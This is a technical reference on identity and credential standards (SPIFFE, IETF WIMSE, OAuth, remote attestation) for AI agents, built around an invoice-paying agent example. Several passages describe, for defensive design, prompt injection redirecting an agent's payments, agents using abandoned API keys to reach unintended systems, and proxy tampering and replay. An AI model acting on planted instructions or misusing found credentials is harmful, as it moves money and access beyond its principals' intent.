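# Identity standards for software agents, and the separate decision about what an agent may do

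## What workload identity is and what an agent adds

Workload identity is a set of techniques that lets a running program prove to other programs which program it is. A workload is running software that does a specific job, such as a company's payroll service or its customer database. It may run as one copy or as hundreds, and a single copy may last a fraction of a second or several years (Salowey, Rosomakho and Tschofenig, 2026, *Workload Identity in a Multi System Environment (WIMSE) Architecture*). Engineers have begun to apply the same techniques to AI agents, programs that use a language model to choose their next step. With an identity check, a payment system can establish which agent is calling it. Whether to make the payment the agent requests is a separate decision, which the identity standards mostly leave to whoever runs the payment system.

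### From shared passwords to issued credentials

Programs, like people, need identities so that others can tell them apart. A salary database, for example, should answer the payroll service but refuse the canteen's menu page. For years companies relied mostly on the network to make this distinction. They put their servers behind a firewall and trusted any program that called from a known address inside it. Joe Beda, a founding engineer of Kubernetes (software that starts programs and spreads them over many machines), thought this too crude, and wrote in *Secure Production Identity Framework For Everyone* (2016) that relying on network rules alone implies that "reachability is authorization". Cloud computing made the approach even weaker, because programs now start, multiply and move between machines within minutes, and an address no longer maps cleanly to one program (Feldman, Fox and colleagues,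 *Solving the Bottom Turtle*, 2020).

The other old method copied how people log in. Administrators created service accounts, which are user accounts that belong to a program, and gave the program a password. Or they gave it an API key, a long string that the program sends with each request. Developers paste these strings into source code that ends up in public repositories. Replacing a leaked string means coordinating updates to every service that uses it, and missing one can cause an outage. A company can lock its secrets in a digital vault, but then each program needs a secret to open the vault. Feldman and colleagues named their book after this regress, using the old story in which the world rests on a turtle, which rests on another turtle, and so on.

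The solution is for the platform that starts a program to vouch for it, since the platform already holds facts about what it started. *Workload Identity Practices* (Schwenkschuster and Rosomakho, 2026) describes how several platforms do this. Kubernetes keeps the name "service account", but its control software signs a token for the program and delivers it as a file. Under SPIFFE, an open standard for workload identifiers and credentials, the program calls a local interface without presenting a secret. The software behind the interface identifies the caller from process attributes, kernel data or the scheduler's labels, and returns a signed credential. Nobody has to type, store or remember anything, so the credential can expire soon and the platform can replace it automatically. Automatically issued credentials can still be long-lived, though. The paper's sample Kubernetes token is valid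 for a year, and its sample SPIFFE token for five minutes.

According to the timeline in Jessup and Feldman's *Intro* (2018), Google built a system of this kind for its own use around 2005, and Netflix later built another. Beda credited Google's system as an inspiration when he drafted SPIFFE in March 2016. He suggested certificates that last an hour or two and explicitly left authorisation out of scope. Engineers who had solved the same problem separately then met at Netflix to agree on a common design. SPIFFE and its reference implementation, SPIRE, were first released in 2017, and the Cloud Native Computing Foundation, which hosts open-source software, accepted the project on 29 March 2018 (CNCF, 2018). SPIFFE covered identity, while OAuth, a framework through which software obtains limited access, often on a user's behalf, covered access rights. Companies combined the two in their own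 ways. The minutes of a November 2023 meeting of the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), the body behind OAuth, record the complaint that customers ran workloads in several clouds and could not reason across the clouds' identity systems (Saxe and Shekh-Yusef, *WimSE BoF at IETF 118*). The IETF formed a working group on Workload Identity in Multi System Environments (WIMSE) on 7 March 2024 (Sheffer, *WG Action*, 2024). Its charter commits it to combining existing standards where it can.

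Much of what follows relies on IETF documents, which differ in standing. Anyone may submit an individual Internet-Draft, which carries no endorsement, expires after six months unless renewed, and is fit to cite only as work in progress. When a working group adopts a draft, the group takes control of the text, but the draft still expires and the group can change or abandon it. An RFC is a finished document that the IETF has approved and published under a permanent number. Some RFCs are standards, while others are only informational.

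The main IETF text on agents, *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization* (Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues, 2026), describes how to apply SPIFFE, WIMSE and OAuth to agents and proposes no new protocols. Six engineers from companies including AWS, OpenAI and Okta wrote it as an individual draft, and by September 2026 the WIMSE group had adopted it under a new name. The group is running late. Its charter set March 2025 for submitting its first proposed standards for approval, but in June 2026 the IETF's *Workload Identity in Multi System Environments (wimse)* page still listed seven active drafts. Anyone building on these texts today should expect details to change.

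### The basic terms

Authentication means checking that a party is who or what it says it is, as when a hotel receptionist compares a guest's face with a passport. Authorisation means deciding whether a party may do what it asks to do. The receptionist can know who a guest is and still refuse to hand over the key to someone else's room. Feldman and colleagues warn SPIFFE users in particular not to confuse the two. SPIFFE automatically gives services an identity as they start up, so a service's ability to authenticate doesn't show that it is allowed to do anything.

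Delegation means giving another party limited authority to act for you while both identities stay visible. Suppose you sign a note that lets a neighbour collect your parcel. The clerk sees your name on the note and the neighbour's on their own identity card. If the neighbour borrowed your card and pretended to be you, that would be impersonation, and the post office's records would show only you. The difference matters to anyone who later has to find out which program made a payment. Salowey and colleagues allow for both delegation and impersonation in workload systems.

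A credential is a signed, expiring document that ties an identifier to a cryptographic key or grants access. Before issuing one, the issuer usually checks evidence about the program and the machine it runs on, a step called attestation.

Credentials also differ in what a thief can do with them. A bearer token works for whoever holds it, like a cinema ticket. Proof of possession requires the sender to show that it also holds a private key that matches the credential, so a thief who has only the credential cannot use it. The sender signs the message with the private key, without revealing the key, and the recipient checks the signature against the public key in the credential. API keys are bearer tokens that are especially risky if stolen, and Kasselman and colleagues call them an antipattern for agents because they are long-lived, hard to replace and convey no identity.

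### What an agent does differently

Kasselman and colleagues define an agent as a workload that interacts repeatedly with a language model and a set of tools until it reaches a stopping condition. A tool here is anything outside the agent that it can call, such as a database, a mailbox or a payment service.

1. The agent gathers text: the user's request, its standing instructions, descriptions of the available tools, and the results of earlier calls.
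2. It sends this text, the context, to the language model.
3. The model's output indicates which tool to call.
4. The agent makes the call.
5. The tool returns a result, which the agent can add to the context before the loop starts again.

The agent program and the language model are thus separate, and usually run as separate services. The program holds the credentials and makes the calls, so the program, not the model, needs an identity. (Older identity documents also use the word "agent" for a small helper on each machine that fetches credentials for the workloads there and does not use a language model.) On the network, an agent looks like any other workload, so it can have a name and a credential in the same way.

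An agent differs from an ordinary service in how its next action is determined. An ordinary invoice service also responds to its input, but a programmer wrote down in advance what follows from each value, so someone reading the code could list every kind of call the service will ever make. An agent's programmer fixes the set of tools, but which tool the agent calls next, and with what amount and account number, depends on how a model responds to the text it has just read. Some of that text comes from strangers. If a supplier adds a line about "new bank details" to an invoice, that line enters the same context as the user's instructions.

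In prompt injection, an attacker plants text to redirect a model. Kasselman and colleagues forbid giving the language model access to the agent's credentials, so that planted text cannot cause the model to disclose or misuse them. The rule is sound, but it does not secure the agent's actions. An attacker who can influence which tool the model chooses does not need to steal credentials, because the agent will make the call under its own valid identity.

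This also complicates the usual way of setting permissions, which is to grant a program the least it needs for its job. In *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a concept paper from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) ask the public how to establish least privilege for an agent whose required actions "might not be fully predictable when deployed". Someone setting permissions for an ordinary service can work them out from its code, but for an agent they have to guess which calls its tasks will require. If the guess is too generous, the agent will be able to make calls that no task required.

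### An agent that pays invoices

Suppose Alice works at Acme and is allowed to pay invoices of up to €10,000. She has an agent that reads incoming invoices and calls a payment service on her behalf. The agent's name is `spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice`, where `acme.example` is the trust domain, the set of workloads whose identities Acme issues under one authority.

| | Figure |
|---|---|
| Alice's limit | €10,000 per invoice |
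| The agent's limit | €5,000 per payment |
| The agent's pace | one payment every 10 seconds |
| Workload credential | lasts 60 minutes, renewed after 30 |
| Access token | lasts 5 minutes |

Of the last two documents in the table, the agent uses the workload credential to prove which program it is, while the access token, which it obtains through OAuth, represents what it may do for Alice. Renewing the workload credential halfway through its lifetime leaves 30 minutes to try again if the issuing service is down. No standard sets these lifetimes. Kasselman and colleagues require agent credentials to have an expiry time and recommend a short one, but they don't give a number.

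The agent's limit is half of Alice's, but it applies to each payment separately. At one payment every 10 seconds, the agent can make 360 payments an hour. At €5,000 each, they total €1.8 million, and none exceeds the limit.

### Behavioural authorisation

An ordinary access check settles whether a kind of request is permitted to a given party. Salowey and colleagues list what usually goes into it: whether the information that accompanies the request is genuine, whether the caller has the right role and attributes, and whether the request satisfies rules about such things as the type of action, the place or the time of day. Put as a function, with the action including details such as the amount:

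permit = *f*(party, action, resource, conditions)

Behavioural authorisation means deciding whether this particular action should go ahead, given the task, what the agent has read and what it has done so far. It takes three more inputs:

permit = *g*(party, action, resource, conditions, **task, context, history**)

The term is this reference's own usage and does not come from SPIFFE, WIMSE or OAuth.

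For example, Alice's agent might ask to pay a supplier €4,800. The ordinary check permits this because the caller is the invoice agent, it acts for Alice, she may make payments, and the sum is under €5,000. But the task might show that Alice asked only for the invoices due this week, while this one is due next month, so the payment is outside what she wanted. The context might show that the account number came from an email the agent read a minute ago and not from Acme's supplier records. The history might show two earlier payments of €4,800 to the same supplier for the same bill. The three payments would total €14,400, which is more than Alice herself may pay on one invoice, even though no single request broke a rule.

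Salowey and colleagues also describe authorisation in WIMSE as context-aware, but by "security context" they mean facts about where a request came from: the user behind it, the software and hardware involved, and the processing it has already been through. Those facts would show that the request came from Alice's agent, but they don't include the email with the new account number.

The boundary between the two checks is also not perfectly sharp. A bank that caps a card's daily withdrawals already uses history, and a payment service could catch the three instalments above by adding up what it has paid on each bill. Such totals are easy to write into rules. The task is harder to express as a rule because users normally state it in ordinary language, and Kasselman and colleagues leave translating that language into permissions out of scope.

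## Naming the agent and issuing its credential

Before Acme can issue a credential to its invoice agent, it has to decide what the name on the credential refers to. The name `spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice` could refer to the software, one running copy of it, the copy that works for Alice, or a second agent that the first one started to read a single PDF. An administrator writing a rule that the invoice agent may call the payment service needs a name that every copy shares and that lasts for years, but an engineer investigating a wrong payment needs to know which copy made it.

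### Software, instance, operator or sub-agent

OAuth has mostly used one name for both purposes. A program registers under a client identifier with the server that issues access tokens, and the same string appears in its tokens. This caused little trouble while clients were long-lived servers that people configured by hand. *client instances are actors not new clients* argues that using one name fails for fleets of agents, in which copies start and stop continuously, often on customers' own machines. If a token carries only the client identifier, an investigator cannot find out which copy acted or which key it used.

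The OAuth and WIMSE working groups discussed the problem of identifying agents in a joint session at IETF 127 in San Francisco in November 2026. In *What Exactly Are We Identifying When We Identify an AI Agent?*, Flanagan (2026) reports that engineers have not always distinguished the identity of a piece of software from that of a particular instance. Flanagan adds that what to identify depends on the purpose. Working out who is liable for an overspent budget takes different information from blocking malicious traffic, and a service may sometimes not need to identify the agent at all.

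McGuinness (2026), in *OAuth 2.0 AI Agent Instance Profile*, proposes keeping one client identifier for the platform and adding fields for the instance, including the model and the runtime environment. McGuinness allows "instance" to mean a session, the execution of one task, or a runtime, so the term still needs a definition. For example, an invoice agent that runs all week and works through 40 tasks is one runtime but 40 task executions. Instance names suit records better than permission rules, because an administrator would have to update any rule that used them each time a new instance started.

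In *WIMSE Applicability for AI Agents*, Huawei engineers Ni and Liu (2026) propose a "dual-identity credential" that holds the identifiers and public keys of both the agent and its owner. In their example, a campus network would treat an unknown agent as a guest. If the credential also names an employee in research and development, the network can give the agent that department's access. The owner approves the agent's credential request by signing it. This adds a human check, but a compromised agent may persuade its owner to sign a malicious request.

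Naming the operator in the agent's credential seems to do Acme more harm than good. If the agent works for Alice in the morning and Bob in the afternoon, it needs two credentials, and every service it calls learns whom it is working for. Flanagan is particularly concerned about identifiers that let separate services piece together one person's activities. Acme can instead name Alice in the access token and send that token only to the services that need to know.

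Sub-agents, which an agent starts to handle part of a task, raise the same question. If they share their parent's name, the payment service cannot tell whether a request came from the invoice agent or from the sub-agent that was only supposed to read PDFs. Separate names solve this as long as they are easy to create. *Workload Authorization Grant* (Carleton, 2026) describes platforms where they are not. These platforms host many agents for each customer, and the person who creates an agent usually has no authority to arrange credentials at the services it will use, so companies end up sharing one credential among all their agents.

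Carleton's remedy is for the platform to sign a statement for each agent. An administrator configures a service once to trust the platform's issuer, and the service then accepts agents it has never encountered. Each agent has an identifier that the platform never changes or reassigns, even if a user renames the agent. The draft is exploratory, and several sections are still blank. It covers only agents that act on their own behalf, so it wouldn't fit Alice's agent as it stands.

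Kasselman and colleagues require each agent to have exactly one WIMSE identifier, which may be a SPIFFE identifier and must stay the same for the lifetime of the workload identity. Permission rules, delegations and audit records can then all refer to the same string. The rule doesn't specify whether two copies of the invoice agent count as one agent or two, but a workload may run in many copies, so the natural reading is that they can share a name. Acme could sensibly use one name for the invoice agent's software and another for any sub-agent that needs different permissions, and record an instance identifier in the logs.

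Acme also has to choose the text of the name. A SPIFFE identifier consists of `spiffe://`, a trust domain and a path, and Acme decides what the path means. *WIMSE Workload Credentials* (Campbell, Salowey and colleagues, 2026) allows rules that depend on how a company builds its identifiers, so Acme could apply one rule to everything under `/agents/`. Carleton forbids services to interpret the identifier and requires them to compare the whole string. Acme's own services can reasonably read the path because Acme controls how its paths are built, but an outside supplier's rules could break without warning if Acme reorganised its names.

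### How SPIRE issues the credential

SPIRE has a central server that signs credentials and a helper program on each machine that hands them to workloads. Acme's agent runs on Kubernetes and gets its credential as follows.

1. An administrator creates a registration entry on the server. It assigns the name `spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice` to any program with certain properties, which SPIRE calls selectors. Acme uses `k8s:ns:finance` and `k8s:sa:invoice-agent`, meaning that the program runs in the Kubernetes namespace "finance" under the service account "invoice-agent". The entry also specifies which machines may host the program.
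2. The agent starts and connects to the helper's local interface, the Workload API. It doesn't state its own name.
3. The helper asks the operating system which process is calling, looks up that process's properties and compares them with the registration entries. An entry matches if the process has every selector in it. Extra properties make no difference.
4. The helper generates a pair of keys and sends the public one to the server with a request for a certificate.
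5. The server checks that this machine may host the invoice agent. It then signs a certificate that contains the name, the public key and an expiry time 60 minutes away.
6. The helper gives the agent the certificate, the private key and the trust bundle, which is the set of public certificates that Acme's workloads use to check each other's credentials.
7. After 30 minutes, half the certificate's lifetime, the helper obtains a new certificate with a new key and sends both to the agent over the open connection. The agent doesn't have to restart.

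SPIRE usually carries out steps 4 and 5 in advance, so the credential is ready when the agent asks for it. Ni and Liu describe a similar flow for WIMSE, except that the agent generates its own keys, so the private key never leaves the agent. The agent then signs the request to show that it holds the private key.

Most mistakes happen in the registration entry. If the administrator lists only the namespace "finance", every program in it can obtain the invoice agent's name, including one that only prints reports. This causes no errors or alerts, so someone has to compare the entry with the list of programs that match it. An entry that is too narrow is easier to notice. If it includes the fingerprint of one software release, the next release will get no credential and won't be able to call anything.

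SPIRE also doesn't enforce the rule of one identifier per agent. A process that matches two entries receives two identities, so the administrator has to prevent the overlap. A SPIRE certificate doesn't always distinguish running copies of an agent either, because the helper keeps one certificate and key for each entry. Two copies of the invoice agent on the same machine therefore receive the same certificate and key. If Acme wants to know which copy made a payment, each copy has to log its own instance identifier.

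How much the name is worth depends on the evidence behind steps 3 and 5, which is the business of attestation.

### The invoice agent's credential, field by field

The certificate is one way to write down the agent's identity. WIMSE also defines a Workload Identity Token, which contains much the same facts as a JSON Web Token (JWT), a signed piece of text with named fields. Adapted from the example that Campbell and colleagues give, the invoice agent's token would look like this:

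| Field | Value | Purpose |
|---|---|---|
| `alg` | `ES256` | algorithm of the issuer's signature |
| `kid` | `acme-key-7` | which of the issuer's keys made the signature |
| `typ` | `wit+jwt` | marks this as a Workload Identity Token |
| `iss` | `https://identity.acme.example` | the issuer (recommended, but optional) |
| `sub` | `spiffe://acme.example/agents/invoice` | the agent's name |
| `iat` | 09:00 | time of issue |
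| `exp` | 10:00 | time of expiry |
| `jti` | `wit-58213` | unique number of this token (optional) |
| `cnf` | the agent's public key and its algorithm | the key whose private half the sender must prove it holds |

A real token gives the times in seconds since 1970. None of the fields holds Alice's name, the €5,000 limit or the task.

To check the token, the payment service reads the trust domain, `acme.example`, from the `sub` field. It then verifies the signature with a key that an administrator has already linked to that domain. It must not fetch a key from whatever address appears in `iss`, because an attacker could then set up an issuer, sign a token bearing the invoice agent's name and point the service to the attacker's own key. Campbell and colleagues therefore require a list of accepted issuers wherever a service uses `iss` to find keys.

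SPIFFE calls its credentials SVIDs, short for SPIFFE Verifiable Identity Documents. They overlap with the WIMSE formats:

| Format | Type | What it binds to the name | Bearer token? |
|---|---|---|---|
| X.509-SVID (SPIFFE) | certificate | a public key | no |
| Workload Identity Certificate (WIMSE) | certificate | a public key | no |
| JWT-SVID (SPIFFE) | signed token | an intended recipient, but no key | yes |
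| Workload Identity Token (WIMSE) | signed token | a public key | no |

A Workload Identity Certificate must contain exactly one identifier written like a web address. SPIFFE's X.509-SVID, which uses X.509, the certificate format for secure websites, is compatible with it. SPIFFE also has its own version of the Workload Identity Token, called the WIT-SVID.

A JWT-SVID is simpler to use than the other formats because the agent only has to send it. If someone steals it, only its short lifetime and named recipient limit the damage. The Workload Identity Token is safer, but only if the recipient checks the proof of possession. A payment service that reads the name and skips this check is treating the token as a bearer token, which Campbell and colleagues forbid.

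The certificates are also more mature. Campbell and colleagues list them as widely used in SPIFFE and in production at the vendors Defakto Security and Teleport. In May 2026, the token was in beta in SPIFFE, in alpha at Defakto Security and in research at Teleport. According to the IETF's *WIMSE welcome and chair updates* from July 2026, the credentials draft had reached last call, the working group's final round of comments. For a company that needs something reliable now, certificates are the better starting point, with the token as the option where certificates don't work. Whether they work depends mostly on what is between the agent and the service it calls.

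### Proving possession when the agent makes a call

TLS is the protocol that encrypts connections to secure websites. Normally only the server presents a certificate. In mutual TLS the caller presents one too, and each side uses its private key to prove that the certificate is its own. The payment service reads the agent's name from the agent's certificate and attributes everything that arrives on that connection to that agent.

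The agent also has to check the payment service's identity. It calls an address such as `pay.acme.example`, but the certificate it receives contains a workload identifier. Without a table that links the two, the agent can establish only that the service belongs to Acme. An attacker who had taken over another Acme service, such as the canteen's menu page, could then pose as the payment service. Campbell and colleagues require software to support such a table, but each company has to fill it in.

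Mutual TLS works well when the agent connects directly to the payment service. Many companies, however, place a proxy or load balancer between them. It ends the agent's TLS connection, reads the request and opens a second connection to the payment service, which then receives the proxy's certificate instead of the agent's. The payment service can either trust the proxy to identify the sender or require proof of the sender's identity inside the request.

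To prove that it holds its private key, the agent uses the key to sign a second token, the Workload Proof Token, and sends it with its Workload Identity Token. *WIMSE Workload Proof Token* (Campbell and Schwenkschuster, 2026) specifies that this second token contains the intended recipient, an expiry time, a unique number, and a hash (a short fingerprint) of the identity token. The proof is valid for seconds or minutes, and a proxy can pass it on unchanged.

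But the proof token doesn't cover the body of the request, which contains the amount and the account number. A compromised proxy could replace the supplier's account number with an attacker's, and the proof would still pass the payment service's check. Campbell and Schwenkschuster acknowledge that their format doesn't protect against an actively malicious intermediary.

HTTP Message Signatures close that gap. *WIMSE Workload-to-Workload Authentication with HTTP Signatures* (Salowey and Sheffer, 2026) has the agent sign the main parts of the request, including its path, the identity token and a fingerprint of the body. If the proxy changes one digit of the account number, the fingerprint no longer matches and the payment service rejects the request. The signature leaves out the host name because proxies routinely rewrite it. Instead, the agent signs a separate field for the intended recipient,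 and the payment service compares that field with its own configuration.

The agent can also require a signed response. This matters for payments because a proxy could otherwise change "paid" to "failed", and the agent might pay again. This approach adds complexity, and Salowey and Sheffer consider proof tokens simpler and easier to adapt to systems that don't use HTTP, such as message queues.

The two methods also differ in how they fit with OAuth. Since the August 2026 version, the proof token goes in the request's `Authorization` header, which normally carries the OAuth access token, and a request can have only one such header. Campbell and Schwenkschuster chose this header so that nobody could weaken the proof by adding a bearer token that identifies the caller. Acme would therefore have to send Alice's authority in another header, for example as a transaction token, which carries a request's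 context between internal services. Message signatures leave the `Authorization` header free. Kasselman and colleagues' July 2026 text still describes an older header for the proof token, so an implementation that follows it won't match the newer draft.

Neither method reliably prevents replay, in which an attacker captures a valid request and sends it again. Both drafts recommend that recipients remember the unique numbers they have already received. But Salowey and Sheffer don't require the copies of a service to share that memory, and the signature in their first example is valid for five minutes. During that time, an attacker who controls the proxy could resend a €4,800 payment request to a different copy of the payment service. The service needs its own safeguard, such as refusing to pay the same invoice number twice.

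For Acme, this suggests mutual TLS where the agent connects directly, and message signatures where payments pass through a proxy that Acme doesn't fully trust.

### Static keys, shared logins and leaked credentials

Many companies do none of this. NIST's *Back to the Future*, a post from August 2026, describes developers who give agents API keys, long-lived tokens or a person's own login because that is the quickest way to get something working. The post draws on public comments on NIST's concept paper and on conversations with practitioners. It gives no counts, so it is good evidence of which mistakes people make but not of how common they are.

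If Acme's payment service accepts a static API key, a payment made by someone who stole the key looks the same in the log as one made by the agent, and the key still works after Acme has shut the agent down. An auditor can uncover the problem by asking when the key expires and which program it belongs to, since for many API keys nobody can answer either question. NIST reports that such keys are often left unprotected in configuration files, markdown files and logs. Agents make abandoned keys more dangerous, because an agent looking for a way to finish its task may find one and use it to access systems it was not meant to reach.

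Some older services accept only their own kind of credential. Kasselman and colleagues let the agent exchange its primary credential for one the service accepts. This second credential is weaker, but the agent has to prove its identity to get it, and Acme doesn't have to store it in the agent's files.

Alice might instead give the agent her own password, or run it on her laptop under her account. The agent then impersonates her, and the payment service applies her limit instead of the agent's lower one. The clearest sign of the agent in the log is its pace, because no person approves a payment every 10 seconds for an hour. Acme also can't lock out the agent without locking out Alice. Similarly, if several agents share a credential, the log doesn't show which one acted, and withdrawing the credential stops all of them.

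Credentials can also end up where the language model can read them. A developer may paste a key into the agent's instructions, or a tool may return a configuration file that contains one. The Model Context Protocol, a standard way to connect models to tools, also lets an agent request more information from its user during a task. NIST points out that an agent could use this feature to collect passwords, although the protocol's guidance is not to request sensitive information this way. Once a key is in the model's context, an attacker can try to extract it through prompt injection.

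Acme can fix this by having the agent program attach the credential only after the model has chosen a tool. It can check whether the fix works by searching its saved prompts and model outputs for credentials. Signed tokens in the JWT format normally begin with `eyJ`, so a text search will find many of them. API keys have no common format, so Acme would have to search for each one it has issued.

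## Checking the software and its machine before issuing: attestation

SPIRE gave the invoice agent its name because the process ran under the right service account on an approved machine. That doesn't show that the agent is running the code Acme's engineers wrote, or that nobody has tampered with the machine. Some systems check the software itself and have the hardware sign the results. Engineers call both procedures attestation, so when an agent is described as "attested", it's worth asking what was checked and who vouched for the result.

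### What SPIRE checks

SPIRE attests the machine before it attests any program on it. SPIFFE's *SPIRE Concepts* gives the steps for a virtual machine on Amazon's cloud, AWS:

1. SPIRE's helper obtains a document from AWS that identifies the virtual machine.
2. The helper sends the document to the SPIRE server.
3. The server validates the document, either by itself or through an AWS interface, and may look up further properties such as the machine's tags.
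4. The server issues the helper its own certificate. The helper uses it to fetch the registration entries for programs that may run on that machine.

On Kubernetes, which Acme uses, the helper presents a service account token instead, and the server validates it through a Kubernetes interface, according to SPIFFE's *Configuring SPIRE*. If no platform can identify the machine, an administrator can start the helper with a join token, a password that works once.

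In workload attestation, the helper compares the calling process's properties with the registration entries. The operating system's kernel supplies some of these properties, such as the user account, and the Kubernetes software on the machine supplies the namespace and service account.

All this evidence comes from the platform, so an attacker who controls the kernel can make one program look like another. Anyone allowed to start programs under the "invoice-agent" service account can get the agent's name for their own code. To prevent this, Acme can add the container image (the package of files from which Kubernetes starts the program) to the registration entry. Cofide, a vendor of SPIRE-based software, lists the image among the properties SPIRE can match. The entry should identify the image by a hash of its contents, because a label such as `invoice-agent:latest` may later point to different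 contents.

A hash has to change with every release, though. SPIRL's *Kubernetes Workload Attestor* describes an optional alternative in which the software verifies a signature on the image and the company makes the credential depend on the result. New releases then need a signature but not a new entry.

Operators can also easily hash the wrong file. For ordinary Unix processes, SPIRE's documentation page *Agent plugin* describes a hash of the "workload binary", the file the process is executing. If the invoice agent is a Python script, that file is the Python interpreter, so the hash is the same for every script that interpreter runs.

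### Remote attestation

Remote attestation doesn't depend on the operating system's word. It often uses a trusted execution environment (TEE), an area that the hardware isolates from the rest of the machine. Birkholz, Thaler and colleagues, in *Remote ATtestation procedureS (RATS) Architecture*, an informational RFC, define the roles and messages but no protocol. If Acme ran the invoice agent in a TEE, the process could go like this:

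1. As the machine starts, each layer measures the next by hashing its code. Permanent firmware measures the bootloader, the bootloader measures the kernel, and the kernel can measure the agent.
2. A verifier, a service that Acme trusts to judge the measurements, sends an unpredictable number called a nonce.
3. The machine, in the role of attester, signs the measurements and the nonce with a key that the agent cannot reach. The signed package is the evidence.
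4. The verifier checks the signature with the help of an endorsement, usually a statement from the hardware's manufacturer. It compares the measurements with reference values, such as the hashes of software that Acme has approved.
5. The verifier signs an attestation result, which may be a simple pass or fail or something more detailed.
6. The relying party, such as Acme's credential issuer or its payment service, applies its own rules to the result.

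The result can reach the relying party in two ways. In the passport model, the agent gets the result from the verifier and shows it to each service it calls. In the background-check model, the agent gives its evidence to the service, which forwards it to the verifier. The passport model is convenient for an agent that calls many services, but the result is older each time the agent shows it.

Users still have to trust someone, and it may be the cloud provider again. *Proof-of-Guardrail in AI Agents and What (Not) to Trust from It* (Jin, Duan and colleagues, 2026) uses AWS's version of a TEE, in which Amazon's own software measures the code. Users no longer have to take the developer's word that a particular safety filter ran, but they do have to trust Amazon to measure the code correctly. *Trusted AI Agents in the Cloud* (Bodea, Misono and colleagues, 2025) uses AMD and NVIDIA hardware to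 protect an agent even from a malicious cloud operator, but not from physical attacks or side-channel attacks, which infer secrets from things like timing.

Birkholz and colleagues point out that the machine's state can change immediately after it produces evidence. A nonce shows that the signature is recent, but the signed measurement may be much older. If the machine hashed the agent's code at start-up on Monday, evidence signed on Friday can still contain Monday's hash.

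### Sending attestation along with the identity token

The Workload Identity Token described earlier has no field for measurements. Reddy and Ritz (2026), in *WIMSE Workload Attestation*, note that a workload can have a valid identity, prove possession of its key and still be running in a compromised environment. Several drafts address this gap. In Novak's *RATS for TWI* (2025), a workload in a TEE gets its credential through remote attestation. In other drafts, the services that the workload calls receive the attestation.

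*Carrying Remote Attestation Evidence in Workload Identity Tokens (WIT)* (Liu, Zhu and Jin, 2026) puts the measurements inside the token. The token names the type of TEE and lists hashes of the boot software, the kernel, the configuration and the application. A service can compare these hashes with its approved list in under a millisecond, or follow a link in the token to the full evidence when the stakes are higher. The draft defines the hash format only for Intel's TDX technology and leaves AMD's for later. The example token is valid for an hour, so a service that relies on the embedded hashes could be trusting hour-old measurements.

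Reddy and Ritz propose sending the evidence, or the verifier's result, in a separate HTTP header and leaving the token unchanged. The agent uses the unique number of its Workload Proof Token as the nonce, which ties the evidence to a single request. The evidence must also contain the same public key as the identity token, so an attacker can't attach evidence from a healthy machine to a request from a compromised one. A malicious proxy could delete the header, so a service that requires attestation must reject any request without the header.

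For payments, evidence tied to the request seems worth the extra work. Jin and colleagues measured about 98 milliseconds to generate an attestation, roughly 1% of the 10 seconds between the invoice agent's payments. But Acme can't rely on other companies to support either format. The IETF's June 2026 list shows both drafts as individual submissions that the WIMSE group had not adopted. Liu and colleagues' draft was due to expire in September 2026, and Reddy and Ritz's on 9 December.

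In the July 2026 text of the Agent Identity Management System (AIMS), Kasselman and colleagues use the broader term "posture assessment" for any evaluation of signals about an agent, its software and its environment. The signals may include TEE evidence, the software's build history, facts from Kubernetes or simply a statement by the operator. They can determine whether the agent gets a credential, what name the credential carries and how long it lasts. AIMS requires no particular mechanism, evidence format or verifier.

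AIMS allows this flexibility because provisioning is "very infrastructure dependent," as the IETF's minutes of a June 2026 WIMSE meeting describe it. The minutes suggest device-management software as a source of signals for end users' machines. But two companies can both follow AIMS while one checks hardware signatures and the other accepts an administrator's word, so a supplier that receives a credential from Acme's agent would have to ask which signals Acme checked.

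### Measuring the invoice agent part by part

The agent consists of more than the program that holds its credential, and its parts differ in how well anyone can measure them.

| Part | What to measure | Who can measure it | When the measurement goes stale |
|---|---|---|---|
| Container image | hash or signature of the image | the platform or a TEE | at the next release, or when the agent loads new code |
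| Model on Acme's machines | hash of the weights | the software that loads them, ideally in a TEE | when someone changes the weights or adds an adapter |
| Model at another company | weights that Acme can't see | the provider | whenever the provider changes the model |
| System prompt | hash of the text | the agent program or the layer below it | at any edit |
| Tool list | hash of names, descriptions and local code | the agent program or the layer below it | when a tool is added or a remote service changes |
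| Context | hash of the text so far | the agent program | at the next tool result |

The container image is the easiest part to check, since the platform has it before the agent starts. Its hash doesn't cover settings supplied from outside the image at start-up, which may include the system prompt and the model name.

A model's weights, the numbers it learned in training, can fill many gigabytes. Protecting them usually also means protecting the graphics processor that runs the model. Bodea and colleagues built Omega, which measures an agent's code, model, prompts and any adapters (small add-ons that alter a model's behaviour), and combines their hashes into one attested identity. They found that starting a separate protected virtual machine for each agent takes about 18 seconds, so Omega runs many agents in one virtual machine and repeats only the measurements of parts that can change. They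 report that Omega matches the performance of unprotected deployments.

A model that runs on a phone or laptop is usually too large for the device's trusted execution environment (TEE). *AttestLLM* (2025) leaves the model outside the TEE, hides a watermark in each layer's weights and checks the watermarks. This increased average response time by 8% to 9%, compared with 473% to 626% for running the model entirely inside the TEE.

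A system prompt is short enough to hash before every run. *Agent Trust Infrastructure (ATI)* (2026) does this in a simulation, also checks the model and an approved set of tools, and blocks the run if anything differs. These checks run in the same process as the monitor that relies on them and produce no signed report, so an outside party would have to take the result on trust. An exact hash can also cause false alarms. If Acme inserts today's date into the prompt, the hash changes every day, so Acme should hash the fixed template and check the date separately.

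The tool list is harder to keep current. An agent may acquire tools while it runs, and *Governing Dynamic Capabilities* (2026) warns that an agent attested in a TEE can do so silently. Acme could compare the list's hash with an approved one before each tool call. But if a tool is a remote service, the hash covers only its description, and the company that runs the service can replace the code without changing that description.

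### A model behind another company's API

Suppose the invoice agent sends its context to a model provider over the internet and gets text back. Acme can measure every file on its own machines without learning anything about the model that chose the payment. *Who Governs the Machine?* (2026) points out that an agent can present a correctly issued SPIFFE credential while running a compromised model.

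Acme can at least verify that it has reached the right provider by having the agent check the provider's TLS certificate against one Acme approved in advance. Jin and colleagues suggest putting that check inside the measured code, and they leave the user to decide whether to trust the provider. *Evidence-Bound Gateway-Path Provenance for Third-Party LLM Inference* (2026) extends the evidence by routing requests through an attested gateway. In a test on AWS, 95% of attestation checks took at most 4.8 milliseconds, and 95% of encrypted session setups took at most 4.0 milliseconds. Each step happens once per session. The record named the model as gpt-5.5. The attestation supports the record's account of how the gateway handled the request, but it doesn't cover the provider's weights.

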